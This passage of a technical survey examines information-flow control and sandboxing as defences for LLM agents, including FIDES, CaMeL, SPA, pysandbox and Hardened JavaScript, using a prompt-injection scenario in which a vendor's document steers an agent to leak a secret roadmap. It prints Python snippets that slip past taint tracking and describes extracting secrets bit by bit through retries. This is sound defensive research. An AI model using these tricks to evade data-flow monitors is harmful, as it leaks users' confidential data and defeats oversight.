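The alternative is to put the label in the interpreter itself, which runs every operation. King (2008) proposed this for Python in *Taint Mode in Python 3.0 RC3*, with an extra field in every object. Forgeot d'Arc (2008) replied that the patch was "huge", since apparently every function that returns an object had to change, and that its correctness seemed very hard to check. Developers would also have to repeat the work for each new release of the interpreter.

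Yip, Wang and colleagues nevertheless took this approach in *Improving Application Security with Data Flow Assertions* (2009), which presents RESIN, a modified runtime for PHP and Python. In RESIN, a label is a policy object, which contains code. Their main example is HotCRP, an academic conference management program that could email users a password reminder. It also had a preview mode that displayed outgoing emails in the browser. With preview on, anyone could request a reminder for someone else and read that person's password. Under RESIN, the programmer attaches a policy object to each password. The object contains the owner's address and a short function that permits only emailing the password to that address or disclosing it to the conference chair. When the password is copied into other text, the runtime copies the policy object with it. Before that text leaves the program, a filter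 on the output channel runs the function, which blocks the preview.

RESIN puts filters on all input and output channels by default, including sockets. A policy object attached to the roadmap would therefore stop program B, even though nobody had listed `urlopen`. This is a large advantage over the library, and it takes the programmer little work. Eight lines of RESIN policy caught the same access-control bugs in the MoinMoin wiki that took 2,000 lines to catch with Flume, an operating-system-level system with stronger guarantees. But RESIN, too, assumes that the application is not malicious, and it adds the whole language runtime to the trusted base.

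The runtime approach also seems to be faster. RESIN added 33% to processor time on HotCRP, and IBM Research's *PHP Tainted variables* (2008) reports 1% overhead for simpler taint tracking in PHP. Conti and Russo published no timings, but in Steinhauser and Tůma's tests of the library approach, label tracking alone added 7% to 203%, depending on the application. Their complete tool, which also parses every page, took on average 2.66 times as long as the bare application. These figures come from different programs and workloads, so they support only a rough ranking.

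### Program C, step by step

Program C posts one of two fixed sentences, depending on whether the roadmap contains the word "acquisition". If the roadmap is a labelled string and the library has overridden every method it can, the test `"acquisition" in roadmap` calls the library's `__contains__` method, which can read the label. But the interpreter converts the method's result to a plain `True` or `False`, then jumps to one of the branches without calling the library again.

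| Roadmap | Result of the test | Text posted | Tags on the text |
|---|---|---|---|
| mentions an acquisition | `True` | "Our review will take another week." | none |
| does not mention one | `False` | "Our review is on schedule." | none |

No value derived from the roadmap ever reaches `post_public`, so a check on values has nothing to find. The same trick can copy an entire document:

```python
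copy = ""
for character in roadmap:
    for letter in ALPHABET:
        if character == letter:
            copy += letter
```

If `ALPHABET` holds every character that occurs in the roadmap, `copy` ends up with the same text as the roadmap but no tags, because each character in it came from the constant. One public post of `copy` then reveals the whole roadmap. RESIN also misses this leak, since its policy objects follow only data that a program copies or moves.

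Conti and Russo knew this and argued that implicit flows are mostly harmless in honest code. A programmer can leak data explicitly by forgetting one call to a cleaning function, whereas writing the loop above takes deliberate, rather unnatural work. Whether the argument carries over to agents depends on what the model had read when it wrote the program. A planner that has seen only the user's request resembles an honest programmer who makes mistakes. It could well write program C but has no reason to write the copying loop. If the model has read the vendor's offer, the vendor may in effect be the programmer, in which case the argument fails.

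To catch C, the mechanism must keep the label of the condition for as long as the branch runs and account for what the other branch would have done. An interpreter can do this with a program-counter label. *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) proves a form of noninterference for a small agent language that tracks labels this way. A library without control over branches can use a cruder method and treat everything after the test as secret.

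### FIDES: one label for the conversation

The cruder approach suits an agent that makes one tool call at a time. It has no program variables, and all data passes through the model's conversation. FIDES, the Microsoft planner from *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, labels each message and each tool result, down to single fields such as the subject of an email. Nobody can tell reliably which parts of a conversation influenced a model's reply, so the reply gets the join of everything in the context:

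$$\ell_{\text{reply}} = \ell_1 \sqcup \ell_2 \sqcup \dots \sqcup \ell_n.$$

In the vendor task, the context starts as $(T, L)$, trusted and public. Reading the offer changes it to $(U, L)$, and reading the roadmap changes it to $(U, H)$, untrusted and secret. Every call the model proposes after that counts as untrusted, so the integrity policy blocks even the email to the user.

FIDES avoids this by keeping restrictive data out of the conversation. If a tool result would raise the context's label, the harness stores the result in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. The vendor task then goes as follows:

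1. `read_file` returns the offer, which the harness stores as `#read_file_0` with label $(U, L)$.
2. `read_file` returns the roadmap, which becomes `#read_file_1` with label $(T, H)$.
3. The planner passes both names and a question to `query_llm`, which runs the quarantined model. The answer becomes `#query_llm_0` with label $(U, H)$.
4. The planner calls `send_email` with the user's address and `#query_llm_0` as the body.

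The context is still $(T, L)$ at the last step. A policy that requires a trusted call and a trusted recipient, but allows an untrusted body, permits the email as long as the user may read the roadmap. In program A, the recipient would be a variable with label U, so the harness would refuse the call.

Sometimes the planner must know what a document contains before continuing, for example when the user asks it to add a meeting to the calendar if any email requests one. FIDES lets the planner ask the quarantined model a yes-or-no question and read the answer. The label records that the answer is a Boolean, and a policy may accept it because one bit cannot hold a prompt injection. But the join of two Boolean types is also Boolean, so the label does not show how many such bits the planner has received. The published evaluation did not use this feature.

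That evaluation ran on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. Without labels, 152 attacks on the agent succeeded, but none did once the harness enforced the policies. The table shows the percentage of tasks completed when there was no attack.

| Environment | No policy | Policy with context label only | Policy with FIDES variables |
|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 75.0 | 37.0 | 59.0 |
| Travel | 70.0 | 73.0 | 41.0 |
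| Banking | 98.8 | 37.5 | 52.5 |
| Slack | 93.3 | 20.0 | 47.6 |

Hiding data recovers much of the loss everywhere except in travel, where the policy already let most tools run in an untrusted context and the variables only confused the model. OpenAI's o1, a stronger model, raised the FIDES travel figure to 68%, so some of the loss comes from the planner's limited skill and should shrink as models improve. But the labels were unusually good, because the experimenters marked a field as untrusted if the benchmark plants an attack in it, and a real deployment has no such list of where attacks will appear.

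Microsoft has since added FIDES to its Agent Framework as an experimental feature. According to Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026), a tool the developer forgets to label counts as trusted and public. This default makes adoption easy, but a forgotten label fails open, as in the Python library.

### What FIDES guarantees

FIDES guarantees explicit secrecy. Let $d$ be all the data that the tools can read and write, and write $d_1 =_L d_2$ if two versions agree on everything public. Suppose that a run starting from $d_1$ makes a certain sequence of tool calls, and let $g$ be the combined effect of exactly those calls. Explicit secrecy requires that for every $d_2$

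$$d_1 =_L d_2 \;\Rightarrow\; g(d_1) =_L g(d_2).$$

Replaying the same calls on different secrets must produce the same public result. Noninterference would instead compare the agent's actual runs on those secrets, and the agent might make different calls in each.

Suppose an agent carries out program C one call at a time. The model reads the roadmap in its context and types one of the two sentences. FIDES refuses the post because the sentence inherits the secret label of the context in which the model typed it. Now suppose the agent has a tool `mark_review_delayed()`, which takes no arguments and updates a public page, and calls it only if the roadmap mentions an acquisition. The confidentiality policy checks the labels of arguments, and this call has none. The run also satisfies explicit secrecy, since replaying "read the roadmap, mark the review as delayed" on any other roadmap gives the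 same public page. The vendor still learns the secret by seeing that the call happened.

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* deliberately accepts this leak. Closing it would essentially mean forbidding every publicly visible write after any read of secret data, which would block much ordinary work. The guarantee also excludes side channels such as timing and the length of network packets, and it depends on correct declarations of what each tool reads and writes.

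### Label creep

Joins only make a label more restrictive, so labels build up during a task until legitimate actions are blocked, a problem known as label creep. In Microsoft's version of FIDES, one untrusted GitHub issue in the context makes the rest of the run untrusted unless the developer explicitly removes it. Agents that work in teams also pass labels to one another.

In *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026) simulated how the layout of such a team affects label creep. They generated 1,000 random tasks, each with 20 tool calls that depended on one another's results, and divided the calls among five agents. Some calls introduced a high-sensitivity label. An agent that received labelled data kept the label permanently and passed it on with everything it sent. If two agents had no direct link, their messages went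 through other agents, which picked up the label too. They measured utility loss as the share of tool calls that introduced a high-sensitivity label or ran under one.

Across nine network layouts, denser networks lost less utility because messages passed through fewer intermediaries. The rank correlation between utility loss and density, the share of possible links that exist, was −0.96. With four sensitive calls per task, and compared with a network that had a direct link wherever the task needed one, a star, in which everything goes through a central agent, lost about 5 percentage points more, and a ring lost about 3 points more. Spreading the work over more agents also reduced the loss, but the number of links to monitor could grow with the square of the number of agents. Giving the sensitive tools to a few dedicated agents helped in every layout.

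The correlation is limited evidence because it compares only the ranking of nine networks and does not measure how much density matters. The gaps of 3 to 5 points suggest a modest effect. The simulation used random graphs as tasks and did not include a language model. Its loss measure also counts every call made under a high label, even one that a real policy would allow, such as emailing the secret summary to a user who is allowed to read it. The more robust finding is that even the ideal layout lost utility, because nothing in the simulation could lower a label.

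### Lowering a label, or avoiding the rise

Lowering a label on purpose is called declassification when it concerns secrecy and endorsement when it concerns trust. Conti and Russo's cleaning functions are a simple case of endorsement, and DjangoChecker's results show that whoever lowers a label has to know where the data will go next. Of the 85 flaws it found, 78 were in text that had been cleaned the wrong way for the place where it ended up. Most often, the application had cleaned text for use in HTML and then put it into a web address. Conti and Russo's library, which drops the tag after cleaning, found none of those 78.

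*APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) ties each exception to a particular use. It describes a monitor for tool calls that responds to a failed check with a list of permitted ways forward. If the data is too restricted for its destination, an approved transformation may produce a cleaner version, for instance by removing personal details. An authority can also approve this one call with exactly these arguments, which leaves the labels unchanged and gives no permission for the next call. Reading more data cannot help, since it can only make the labels stricter. The authority may be a fixed rule, a person or another language model, within limits that the developer sets in advance. If it is a model, an attacker who persuades it gets whatever those limits allow.

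APPA can also prevent the label from rising. The agent starts a temporary copy of its conversation, reads the untrusted document there, and returns only a value from a fixed list of options. The main conversation keeps its old label. A manipulated copy can still pick the wrong option, so Kravchenko and colleagues let the developer decide whether to trust the answer. APPA also treats the output of unlabelled tools as unknown and blocks any call that depends on it until an approved classifier labels that output, which is safer than Microsoft's default.

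In tests on OWASP's AgentThreatBench and simulated office workflows, APPA completed between 64.2% and 91% of tasks, and no attack succeeded in 1,320 guarded runs. These results apply to the policies tested. The corresponding author works at the vendor Archestra. Kravchenko and colleagues describe the guarantee as authorised and audited release, and state that it is not noninterference.

*SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) checks the labels before anything runs. For each request, SPA's planner writes one complete plan, and a checker works out the label of every future value from the labels of the tools that will produce it. The checker also takes into account the conditions that decide whether each step happens. In program C, the public post depends on a test of the secret roadmap, so the checker rejects the plan. The planner cannot try again, because Girrens and Wang did not want it to keep revising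 an unsafe plan until a version got past the checker.

SPA also keeps labels from one request to the next. Suppose a user asks an agent on Monday to save the details of an invoice, and on Tuesday to pay it. If an attacker wrote the account number on the invoice, the number is still untrusted on Tuesday. SPA stores the number with its label and shows the planner only a description of the stored data.

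SPA's label checks reduced the attack success rate to zero on AgentDojo and to 0.2% on a version with several linked requests. They also reduced the share of tasks completed. On AgentDojo it fell from 53.0% to 29.0%, and with linked requests it fell from 62.5% to 35.3%. Most of the rejected plans passed outside data to an action that demanded trusted input, which many legitimate tasks need to do. Checking early prevents a forbidden task from being left half done, but it does not make the labels less restrictive. SPA's checker can examine both branches of a program because its plans are written in a small language with six kinds of step, rather than in Python. A separate interpreter runs them.

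## Attempts to confine untrusted code inside a general-purpose language

An agent program written in Python runs in the same process as labelling libraries and tool wrappers, so it can alter them. A developer might try to fix this by removing dangerous features from the agent's program, so that it can't open files, import networking modules or inspect the harness's objects, but can still call the harness's functions directly and at full speed. Language developers have tried this since the 1990s for web applets, chat bots and plugins. Security engineers call the trusted program the host and the untrusted code the guest.

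### rexec and Bastion

Python's standard library once had two modules for confining untrusted code. `rexec` ran guest code with a limited set of modules and functions, and `Bastion` gave it restricted access to the host's objects. Python's *Restricted Execution* compares the guest's environment to a padded cell whose contents the host chooses. For example, the host could replace the built-in `open` function with a version that could only read files, and only in one directory. The guest would still call `open` in the usual way, so its author had nothing new to learn. Grail, a web browser written in Python, used the modules to run applets, small programs downloaded from the web.

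The interpreter recognised guest code by its table of built-in functions. If the table was not the standard one, the interpreter hid certain attributes of functions, classes and objects that the code could use to escape the cell. This protection was therefore complete only if the list of hidden attributes accounted for every feature of the language.

Python 2.2 made the list badly out of date. It merged the built-in types with the classes that programmers define, which gave programs new ways to inspect objects. In *new features for 2.3?*, Guido van Rossum, Python's creator, quoted a message that attributed most of rexec's vulnerabilities to missing restrictions on these new abilities. He replied that he would like to keep the restricted mode even if it was imperfect, and that the main obstacle was a lack of time to think about it. When another developer suggested that such large changes would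 be rare, van Rossum (2002) answered in *known obvious thing or bug (rexec)?* that "every change is a potential security hole."

Three weeks later he disabled both modules. In the announcement, *Deleting rexec.py and Bastion.py* (2003), he wrote that the Python developers lacked the resources to fix them, and that anyone using them on anonymously submitted code should stop immediately. The decision affected PostgreSQL, whose PL/Python extension let database users write functions in Python and relied on the restricted mode to confine those functions. In the thread *Expect problems with PL/Python and Python version 2.2.3+ & 2.3+* (2003), the PostgreSQL developer Tom Lane concluded that the project would have to reclassify PL/Python as untrusted or remove it.

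Nobody repaired the modules. Hylton (2003) explained in *rexec.py unuseable* that the designers of newer Python features had not taken rexec into account, and that reconciling the two would be very difficult. Python 3 removed rexec, according to the module's documentation.

### pysandbox

Victor Stinner's pysandbox is a better test of this approach than rexec, which may have ended only because nobody had enough time for it. Stinner spent three years on pysandbox. It grew out of a 2010 experiment by a developer known as Tav, who hid sensitive attributes from guest code and challenged Python's core developers to break out. They did so quickly, but Stinner thought the idea was worth pursuing and added more protections. He released version 1.0 in June 2010 and used it for a bot that ran code for visitors to a French Python chat channel. Most of the bot's users were trying to break it.

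The first vulnerability appeared three months later. Stinner fixed it, found another just afterwards, and seven months after that had to fix more. In 2013 a security challenge targeted pysandbox, and the participants found two new escapes in less than a day. Stinner fixed those too, but in *The pysandbox project is broken* (2013) he announced that he now considered the design itself a mistake.

His main reason was the amount of code he had to trust. Guest code could reach almost any part of CPython, the standard Python interpreter, so a single bug anywhere in it could defeat the whole sandbox. This made the interpreter part of the monitor, and it was far too large to meet Anderson's standard: two of its source directories alone held more than 126,000 lines of C. One of the 2013 flaws also convinced him that the problem went beyond bugs, because a built-in function with no obvious connection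 to file access could reveal a file's contents. Blocking the functions that open files was therefore not enough, and he saw no acceptable way to change CPython to prevent such leaks.

Stinner also wrote that people could not use pysandbox in practice for anything more complex than evaluating a sum. Each fix removed something that legitimate code needed, including basic operations like deleting an entry from a dictionary. He could not drop individual protections because the sandbox needed all of them. The host also had no general way to safely give the guest access to one of its objects.

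Stinner had begun to move guest code into a separate process, which allowed memory limits and real timeouts and kept a crash in the guest from bringing down the host. But the two processes could exchange only data that the host had first converted to bytes, and debugging became harder. His final advice was to put the entire Python process in an external sandbox, such as one built with seccomp, a Linux feature that restricts which requests a process may make to the kernel. Coghlan (2013), replying under the same title, agreed that such platform-level mechanisms were the only ones he even "remotely" trusted. He added that even Lua, a much smaller language than Python, is hard to secure inside a host process. Stinner has abandoned pysandbox, which now carries a warning to "run python in a sandbox, not the opposite".

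### Java's Security Manager

Java had a better starting point. Its designers planned for hostile guest code from version 1.0, because web browsers downloaded Java applets from strangers. They built checks into the standard library and put a component called the Security Manager in charge of them. At first, it simply allowed local code to use files and the network and refused applets. Java 1.2 replaced this with separate permissions for each body of code, and OpenJDK's *JEP 411* (2021), a proposal from the project that develops Java, describes how the check worked. Programmers know the method as stack inspection:

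1. Before a library method opens a file or a connection, it asks the Security Manager whether the running code has permission.
2. The Security Manager goes through the call stack, meaning the chain of methods that have started and not yet finished, and looks up the permissions of the code behind each one.
3. If any of that code lacks the permission, the Security Manager raises an error and the operation does not happen.
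4. A library can ask the Security Manager to consider only the library's own permissions for a particular block of code, and not those of the code that called it.

Suppose the agent program from the vendor task were written in Java and had no permission to use the network. Program B, which sends the roadmap by a direct HTTP request, would fail at step 3 because the agent's program is on the stack and lacks permission to open connections, even though the networking library has it. The mail tool also needs the network, so its author would use step 4 to let the agent send email through it.

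Program A would pass for the same reason. The stack shows which code is requesting the connection, but not where the recipient's address came from. The mail tool's author would have to check the address, or the tool would become a confused deputy. Program C would also pass if the tool that posts on the public page used step 4, because both of its sentences go through a method that the program may call.

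Most of OpenJDK's reasons for retiring the Security Manager concern the work of maintaining it and its lack of use. Java 1.0 had only eight core packages, but as the library grew, its developers had to maintain dozens of permissions and hundreds of checks, and consider the Security Manager in every new feature. Permissions could also combine in surprising ways, so that a series of harmless operations had an effect that should have required a stronger permission.

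Application developers found the Security Manager hard to use. To restrict file reading to one directory, a developer also had to list every other protected operation the program performed, because the Security Manager refused any that lacked a permission. Step 2 made this worse, because an application had to hold every permission its libraries needed, even for operations it never performed itself, unless the library authors had used step 4 correctly. The easiest solution was to grant all permissions, which left the program unconfined. The checks were also slow enough that Java left the Security Manager off by default for programs run from the command line.

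Java 17 deprecated the Security Manager in 2021. Oracle's *JEP targeted to JDK 24* (2024) announced JEP 486, a proposal to disable it permanently, and Oracle's *The Security Manager Is Permanently Disabled* confirms that JDK 24 did so. A program that tries to turn it on now stops with an error, and Oracle plans to remove the remaining interfaces in a later release. Oracle directs users to containers, virtual machines and operating-system sandboxes instead.

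This is weaker evidence against in-language confinement than the Python cases are. OpenJDK argues partly that the threat of malicious code receded when browsers stopped running applets, and agents bring that threat back. But the complaints about permissions would apply to agents too. A developer would have to work out which permissions each generated program and each library it depends on needs, and an agent may write a different program for every request.

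### Figma's plugins

Figma, a design tool that runs in the browser, lets outside developers write plugins in JavaScript. It first ran them in the Realms shim, a JavaScript library made by Agoric. The shim ran plugins on the browser's own JavaScript engine, so they were as fast as any other JavaScript and developers could use the browser's built-in debugger.

On 14 September 2019 someone disclosed a vulnerability in the shim through a public GitHub issue, and researchers privately reported more two days later. Figma's *An update on plugin security* (2019) describes how the company stopped approving new plugins at once and installed Agoric's fix within three days. Figma also blocked updates to existing plugins, because updates reached every open copy of Figma immediately and a plugin's author might have learned of a flaw. An audit found no evidence that any published plugin had exploited the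 vulnerabilities.

By 25 September Figma had replaced the shim with QuickJS, a separate JavaScript engine written in C and compiled to WebAssembly, which browsers run in its own area of memory. Figma kept QuickJS even though Agoric had fixed every known flaw in the shim. Those flaws all arose because the shim could confuse objects from inside the sandbox with objects from outside it, which was possible because the same engine ran both kinds of code. QuickJS objects look so different from the browser's that the two cannot be confused.

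Figma gave up some speed for this. In *Figma Plugins*, a developer of mapping plugins later complained that they still ran too slowly, though mapping tools also process more data than most drawing tools do. The same design is also used for agents. *Running Python code in a sandbox with MicroPython and WASM* (Willison, 2026) describes a package that runs MicroPython, a small version of Python, inside WebAssembly. A plugin uses the package to run code for a data-analysis agent.

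### Why fixing holes does not end

A host process holds things that an attacker wants, such as open files, passwords and functions that use the network. When guest code runs in the same process, little more than the lack of a direct reference keeps it from using them, and modern languages offer many ways to get a reference. One is reflection, the ability of a program to examine and change its own objects and code, which is meant to let debuggers and testing tools reach data and code that an object normally hides. Any object that the host shares with the guest may therefore let the guest gain the host's authority.

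The defender has to find and close every path because an attacker needs only one. Python Wiki's *Sandboxed Python* warns that plugging holes one at a time usually leaves others that nobody thought of, and that real security has to be part of the overall design. New language features keep adding paths, as those in Python 2.2 did, because their designers are usually thinking about convenience and speed. Each fix also takes a feature away from legitimate programs. Agents make the defender's job harder, since a manipulated model can write one program after another and use the error messages to improve the next attempt.

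These attempts show how badly confinement within a language goes when the language was not designed for it and the defender starts from the full language and removes features. They don't prove that confinement is impossible. Safe Haskell, a restricted mode of the Haskell compiler, benefits from a language whose types already separate pure computation from actions on the outside world. JavaScript has a more surprising counterexample.

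### Hardened JavaScript

SES is a library that turns ordinary JavaScript into a stricter version called Hardened JavaScript, which its developers have proposed to the language's standards committee. It still lets host and guest share objects, but neither can change them. Its `lockdown` function freezes the built-in objects that every program can reach, such as the prototypes from which arrays and functions inherit their methods. After that, programs cannot replace these methods to interfere with one another, or use the built-in objects to pass messages.

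Guest code then runs in a compartment, which has its own global variables and starts with no ambient authority. For instance, the browser's `fetch` function does not exist there unless the host supplies it. Compartments also lack the current time and random numbers by default, because programs could use them to communicate secretly. The host can pass the guest an object as a capability, after using `harden` to freeze the object and everything reachable from it through its properties. The guest can still call a frozen object's methods, so it can send email if the host supplies a frozen mail tool.

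A JavaScript version of program B would fail in a compartment without `fetch`, but programs A and C would still run.

SES is meant to run third-party code written in JavaScript's strict mode safely, and to prevent programs from observing or affecting one another until someone connects them. Agoric and the cryptocurrency wallet MetaMask use it in systems that run plugins or smart contracts and limit the damage from compromised software packages. Both would be attractive targets for attackers, so their reliance on SES is some evidence that it is secure, though not proof. SES is still under development in 2026.

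SES avoids pysandbox's worst difficulties because it mostly removes authority and leaves ordinary computation working. According to its documentation, most existing JavaScript libraries can run on it. Confinement is also easier in JavaScript than in Python because the JavaScript language itself has no functions for opening files or connections. The browser or server adds them as separate objects, which SES can withhold. But SES still depends on the JavaScript engine working correctly, and its developers have to check each new language feature for objects that SES must freeze.

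### RestrictedPython

RestrictedPython is a long-lived Python project with more modest aims. It replaces Python's `compile` function with one that turns the guest's source code into bytecode for the ordinary interpreter, but raises an error if the code uses anything outside a permitted subset of the language. The host also supplies a limited set of built-in functions and its own versions of the operations that read and set attributes, so that a policy can decide which attributes the guest may use. Compiling the code this way is not enough by itself, because the compiled code can still call any library that the host leaves accessible.

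The best-known users of RestrictedPython are Zope, a web application server, and Plone, a content management system built on it. Plone's *Sandboxing and RestrictedPython* says that scripts and page templates edited through Zope's web interface run in restricted mode, with a security check on every function call, while add-ons installed by a developer run as normal Python. Zope also has an interpreter that wraps the host's objects in proxies. According to untrustedpython's *Untrusted interpreters*, guest code can reach the outside only through proxied functions, and the results are also wrapped in proxies unless they are basic values. This gives Zope a systematic way to share objects with guest code, which pysandbox never had.

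RestrictedPython's developers still maintain it and released version 8.2 in May 2026. It supports CPython 3.10 to 3.14 but no other Python implementation. They describe it as "not a sandbox system or a secured environment" and advise the host to take further security measures. The project's survival shows that a restricted subset can be useful for small scripts by people with an account on the system. It is much weaker evidence that a subset is suitable for running whatever a manipulated model may write.

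### smolagents' local executor

Hugging Face's smolagents is a library for agents that act by writing Python. An earlier version of its documentation page *Secure code execution* describes how the library's local executor parses the agents' code into a syntax tree and carries out each operation itself, instead of passing the code to the standard interpreter. The executor refuses any operation that its developers have not defined and any import that is not on a list of permitted modules. It also limits the number of operations to stop infinite loops.

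This comes closer to refusing by default than pysandbox did. It would stop program B as written, because the networking module is not on the default list, but it would let A and C run. Such checks are useful against the mistakes of an honest model. Hugging Face reported using the executor on varied tasks without ever observing any damage.

The documentation said the executor was "certainly not watertight", and that no local Python sandbox could be. A program can misuse a module it is permitted to use, for example by filling the disk with images through an image library. Some harmless-looking modules also contain references to dangerous ones. In 2025 the US National Vulnerability Database published *CVE-2025-5120 Detail*, which describes a flaw in version 1.14.0 that let guest code escape the executor and run arbitrary code on the host.

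Hugging Face's current documentation, *Python code executors*, says that the local executor "is not a security sandbox". For untrusted code, it recommends a remote executor, which runs the program in a Docker container or on a cloud service such as E2B or Modal.

The executor controlled each statement but did not isolate the guest, because it is a Python program inside the host process and handles ordinary Python objects. When guest code calls a method on one of these objects, the standard interpreter runs that method with the host's full authority. QuickJS in Figma's browser tab is also an interpreter, but it has its own objects and memory. Monty, an interpreter written in Rust for agents' programs, also keeps its values separate from the host's Python values.

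A remote executor creates this separation by running the program elsewhere, and like Stinner's subprocess it can exchange only data converted to bytes. Python's usual format for this, pickle, can run arbitrary code on the machine that reads it, so a malicious result could attack the host even if the sandbox had confined the program. Smolagents therefore uses JSON by default, which can carry only data, and raises an error for any object it cannot safely convert.

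## Interpreters built for the agent's programs

An interpreter built for agents can go further than the smolagents executor by keeping its own values and leaving out every operation that the policy doesn't cover. The program then cannot express an action that skips the check, so mediation is complete for everything the program does. Because the interpreter computes every value itself, it can also record where each one came from.

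CaMeL, from Google DeepMind, limits the operations a program can perform and tracks its data. Monty, from Pydantic, limits operations but doesn't track data. LLMbda, a research language, tracks data and comes with a machine-checked proof that the tracking works.

### CaMeL

CaMeL builds on the dual-LLM pattern, which Simon Willison proposed in 2023. In that pattern, a planner model directs a quarantined model and refers to untrusted text only by names such as `$email-summary-1`. *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (Willison, 2025) describes a flaw that CaMeL's developers found in this pattern. Suppose a user asks the agent to send Bob the document he requested in the last meeting, and Bob's address is in the meeting notes. The planner never reads the notes, so an injection in them cannot redirect it. But the quarantined model reads them, and the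 injection can make it return the attacker's address. The plan then runs as written and sends the document to the attacker, as in program A.

CaMeL keeps both models and puts an interpreter between them:

1. The planner model reads the user's request and writes a program in a restricted version of Python, a language that models already write well.
2. The interpreter parses the program into a syntax tree and evaluates the tree node by node. The tools appear in the program as functions.
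3. To extract something from untrusted text, the program calls the quarantined model with a question and the type of answer it needs, such as an email address.
4. The interpreter attaches tags to every value, which record the value's sources and who may read it. A value computed from several others inherits the restrictions of all of them.
5. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy function on the arguments and their tags. The function can allow the call, refuse it or ask the user.

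In CaMeL, these tags are called capabilities, but holding one doesn't grant any right. The required answer type gives some protection, since an email address can't contain a paragraph of instructions. The address can still be the wrong one, though, and the tags are meant to catch that error.

Willison also points out that this design helps privacy, because the planner's provider sees the user's request but none of the documents, and the quarantined model can be a smaller one running on the user's own machine.

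### Rules for an assignment, a call and a branch

An interpreter that tracks labels stores a label with every variable. It also keeps a program-counter label, written $pc$, for the data that decided whether the current statement runs. Garby and colleagues trace this idea to work by Denning and Denning in 1977. $pc$ starts at the lowest label, because only the user's request has shaped the program so far. Below, $\ell(x)$ is the label of $x$.

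An assignment `x = e` gives the variable the label of the expression, joined with the program-counter label:

$$\ell(x) := \ell(e) \sqcup pc.$$

A constant assigned inside a secret branch therefore becomes secret.

For a call `r = f(a1, ..., an)`, the interpreter first runs the policy for `f` on the arguments, their labels and $pc$. If the policy allows the call, the result gets the label

$$\ell(r) := pc \sqcup \ell_f \sqcup \ell(a_1) \sqcup \dots \sqcup \ell(a_n),$$

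where $\ell_f$ is the label of whatever source the tool reads. Built-in operations such as joining two strings follow the same rule, with the lowest label for $\ell_f$ and no policy.

A branch `if e:` runs the chosen side with a higher program-counter label,

$$pc' = pc \sqcup \ell(e),$$

and restores the old one afterwards. A loop does the same on every pass.

### The test programs, line by line

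Suppose that `read_file` tags documents by folder. Files in the inbox come from the vendor and anyone may read them, while internal files come from the company and only the user may read them. The policy for `send_email` requires that no outsider is a source of the address and that the recipient may read the body. The benign program then produces these tags:

| Statement | Sources | Permitted readers |
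|---|---|---|
| `offer = read_file(...)` | vendor | anyone |
| `roadmap = read_file(...)` | company | the user |
| `question = "How does ..."` | none | anyone |
| `summary = ask_model(question, offer, roadmap)` | vendor, company | the user |

The last line sends `summary` to `USER`. The harness supplied that address, so no outsider is among its sources. The user is allowed to read the body, and $pc$ stays at the lowest label because the program has no branches. The interpreter therefore allows the email to be sent.

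Program A adds the line `address = ask_model(..., offer)`, and the result has the vendor as a source. The policy blocks the send because the vendor is among the sources of `to`. A more lenient policy, like the one in Willison's account of CaMeL, allows sending to any address the user already trusts and requires the user's approval for any other. Under that policy, the vendor can still choose among the trusted addresses, and a user who approves every request also lets A send to the others.

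Program B stops at its first line because the interpreter has no networking module to import. Even if a developer supplied a function for web requests, the result of `roadmap.encode()` would still carry the roadmap's tags, because the call rule labels the result of every method. In Conti and Russo's library, the same conversion to bytes silently removed the label.

Program C goes as follows:

1. The test `"acquisition" in roadmap` gives `True` or `False`, with the company as its source and the user as its only permitted reader.
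2. The `if` statement raises $pc$ to those tags.
3. The sentence to post is a constant that anyone may read, but the call to `post_public` runs under the raised $pc$. The policy refuses it, because the public would learn something that only the user may know.
4. The `else` side runs under the same $pc$ and gets the same refusal.

The program posts nothing, whichever version of the roadmap it reads. The restriction applies only inside the branch, so a program that used the test only to choose the wording of a private note could still post a fixed sentence afterwards. A guard around tool calls would block that post. The branch rule also catches the loop that copied the roadmap letter by letter, because each `copy += letter` runs in a branch that depends on the roadmap.

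### The branch that does not run

These rules still have a hole. Garby and colleagues found it in CaMeL's interpreter, which blocks a direct leak like program C but not this rearrangement of it:

```python
waiting = True
flag = True
if "acquisition" in roadmap:
    waiting = False
if waiting:
    flag = False
if flag:
    post_public("Our review will take another week.")
```

If the roadmap mentions an acquisition, the first branch sets `waiting` to `False` and labels it secret. The second branch doesn't run, so `flag` stays `True` and public. The third test is therefore public, and the post goes out. If it doesn't, `waiting` stays `True` and public, the second branch sets `flag` to `False`, and nothing is posted. No check fails in either case, yet whether the post appears reveals the secret. An interpreter that raises labels only on the branch it takes cannot label an assignment it skips.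 Fenton described this leak in 1974.

Austin and Flanagan's remedy from 2009 adds a condition to the assignment rule. The program may change an existing variable only if

$$pc \sqsubseteq \ell(x),$$

using the variable's old label. In the example, `waiting = False` would change a public variable in a secret branch, so the interpreter stops the program there. An honest program can trip over this rule too, unless its author marks the variable as secret from the start.

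Stopping the program also leaks information, because the program stops only if the roadmap mentions an acquisition. Most information-flow systems accept a leak of one bit per run. In CaMeL the leak can grow, because the interpreter runs inside an ordinary Python loop that does no tracking. When a program fails, the loop passes the error to the planner, which writes another program. The new program starts with clean tags even though it depends on the earlier failure. By changing the test each time, the planner can extract the whole secret one bit at a time. CaMeL censors the error messages to limit this, but without a formal guarantee.

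### LLMbda and its theorem

Garby and colleagues designed LLMbda so that the tracking covers the retry loop and the model's conversation as well as the agent's program. LLMbda extends the lambda calculus, a minimal language built from functions, with operations on a conversation. A program can send a prompt and use the reply, clear the conversation, or work in a temporary copy of it. A quarantined model can be written as a short function that copies the conversation, clears the copy, asks a question there and returns the answer.

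LLMbda, like FIDES, labels the conversation with the join of its messages' labels. If the model replies with code, that code runs with the conversation's label as its $pc$. A model that has read the vendor's offer can therefore write any program, but everything that program computes counts as untrusted. LLMbda also applies Austin and Flanagan's condition to the conversation, so a program cannot add a message to a public conversation from inside a secret branch. LLMbda needs no separate rule for branches because a condition selects one of two functions, and the selected function runs under the condition's label.

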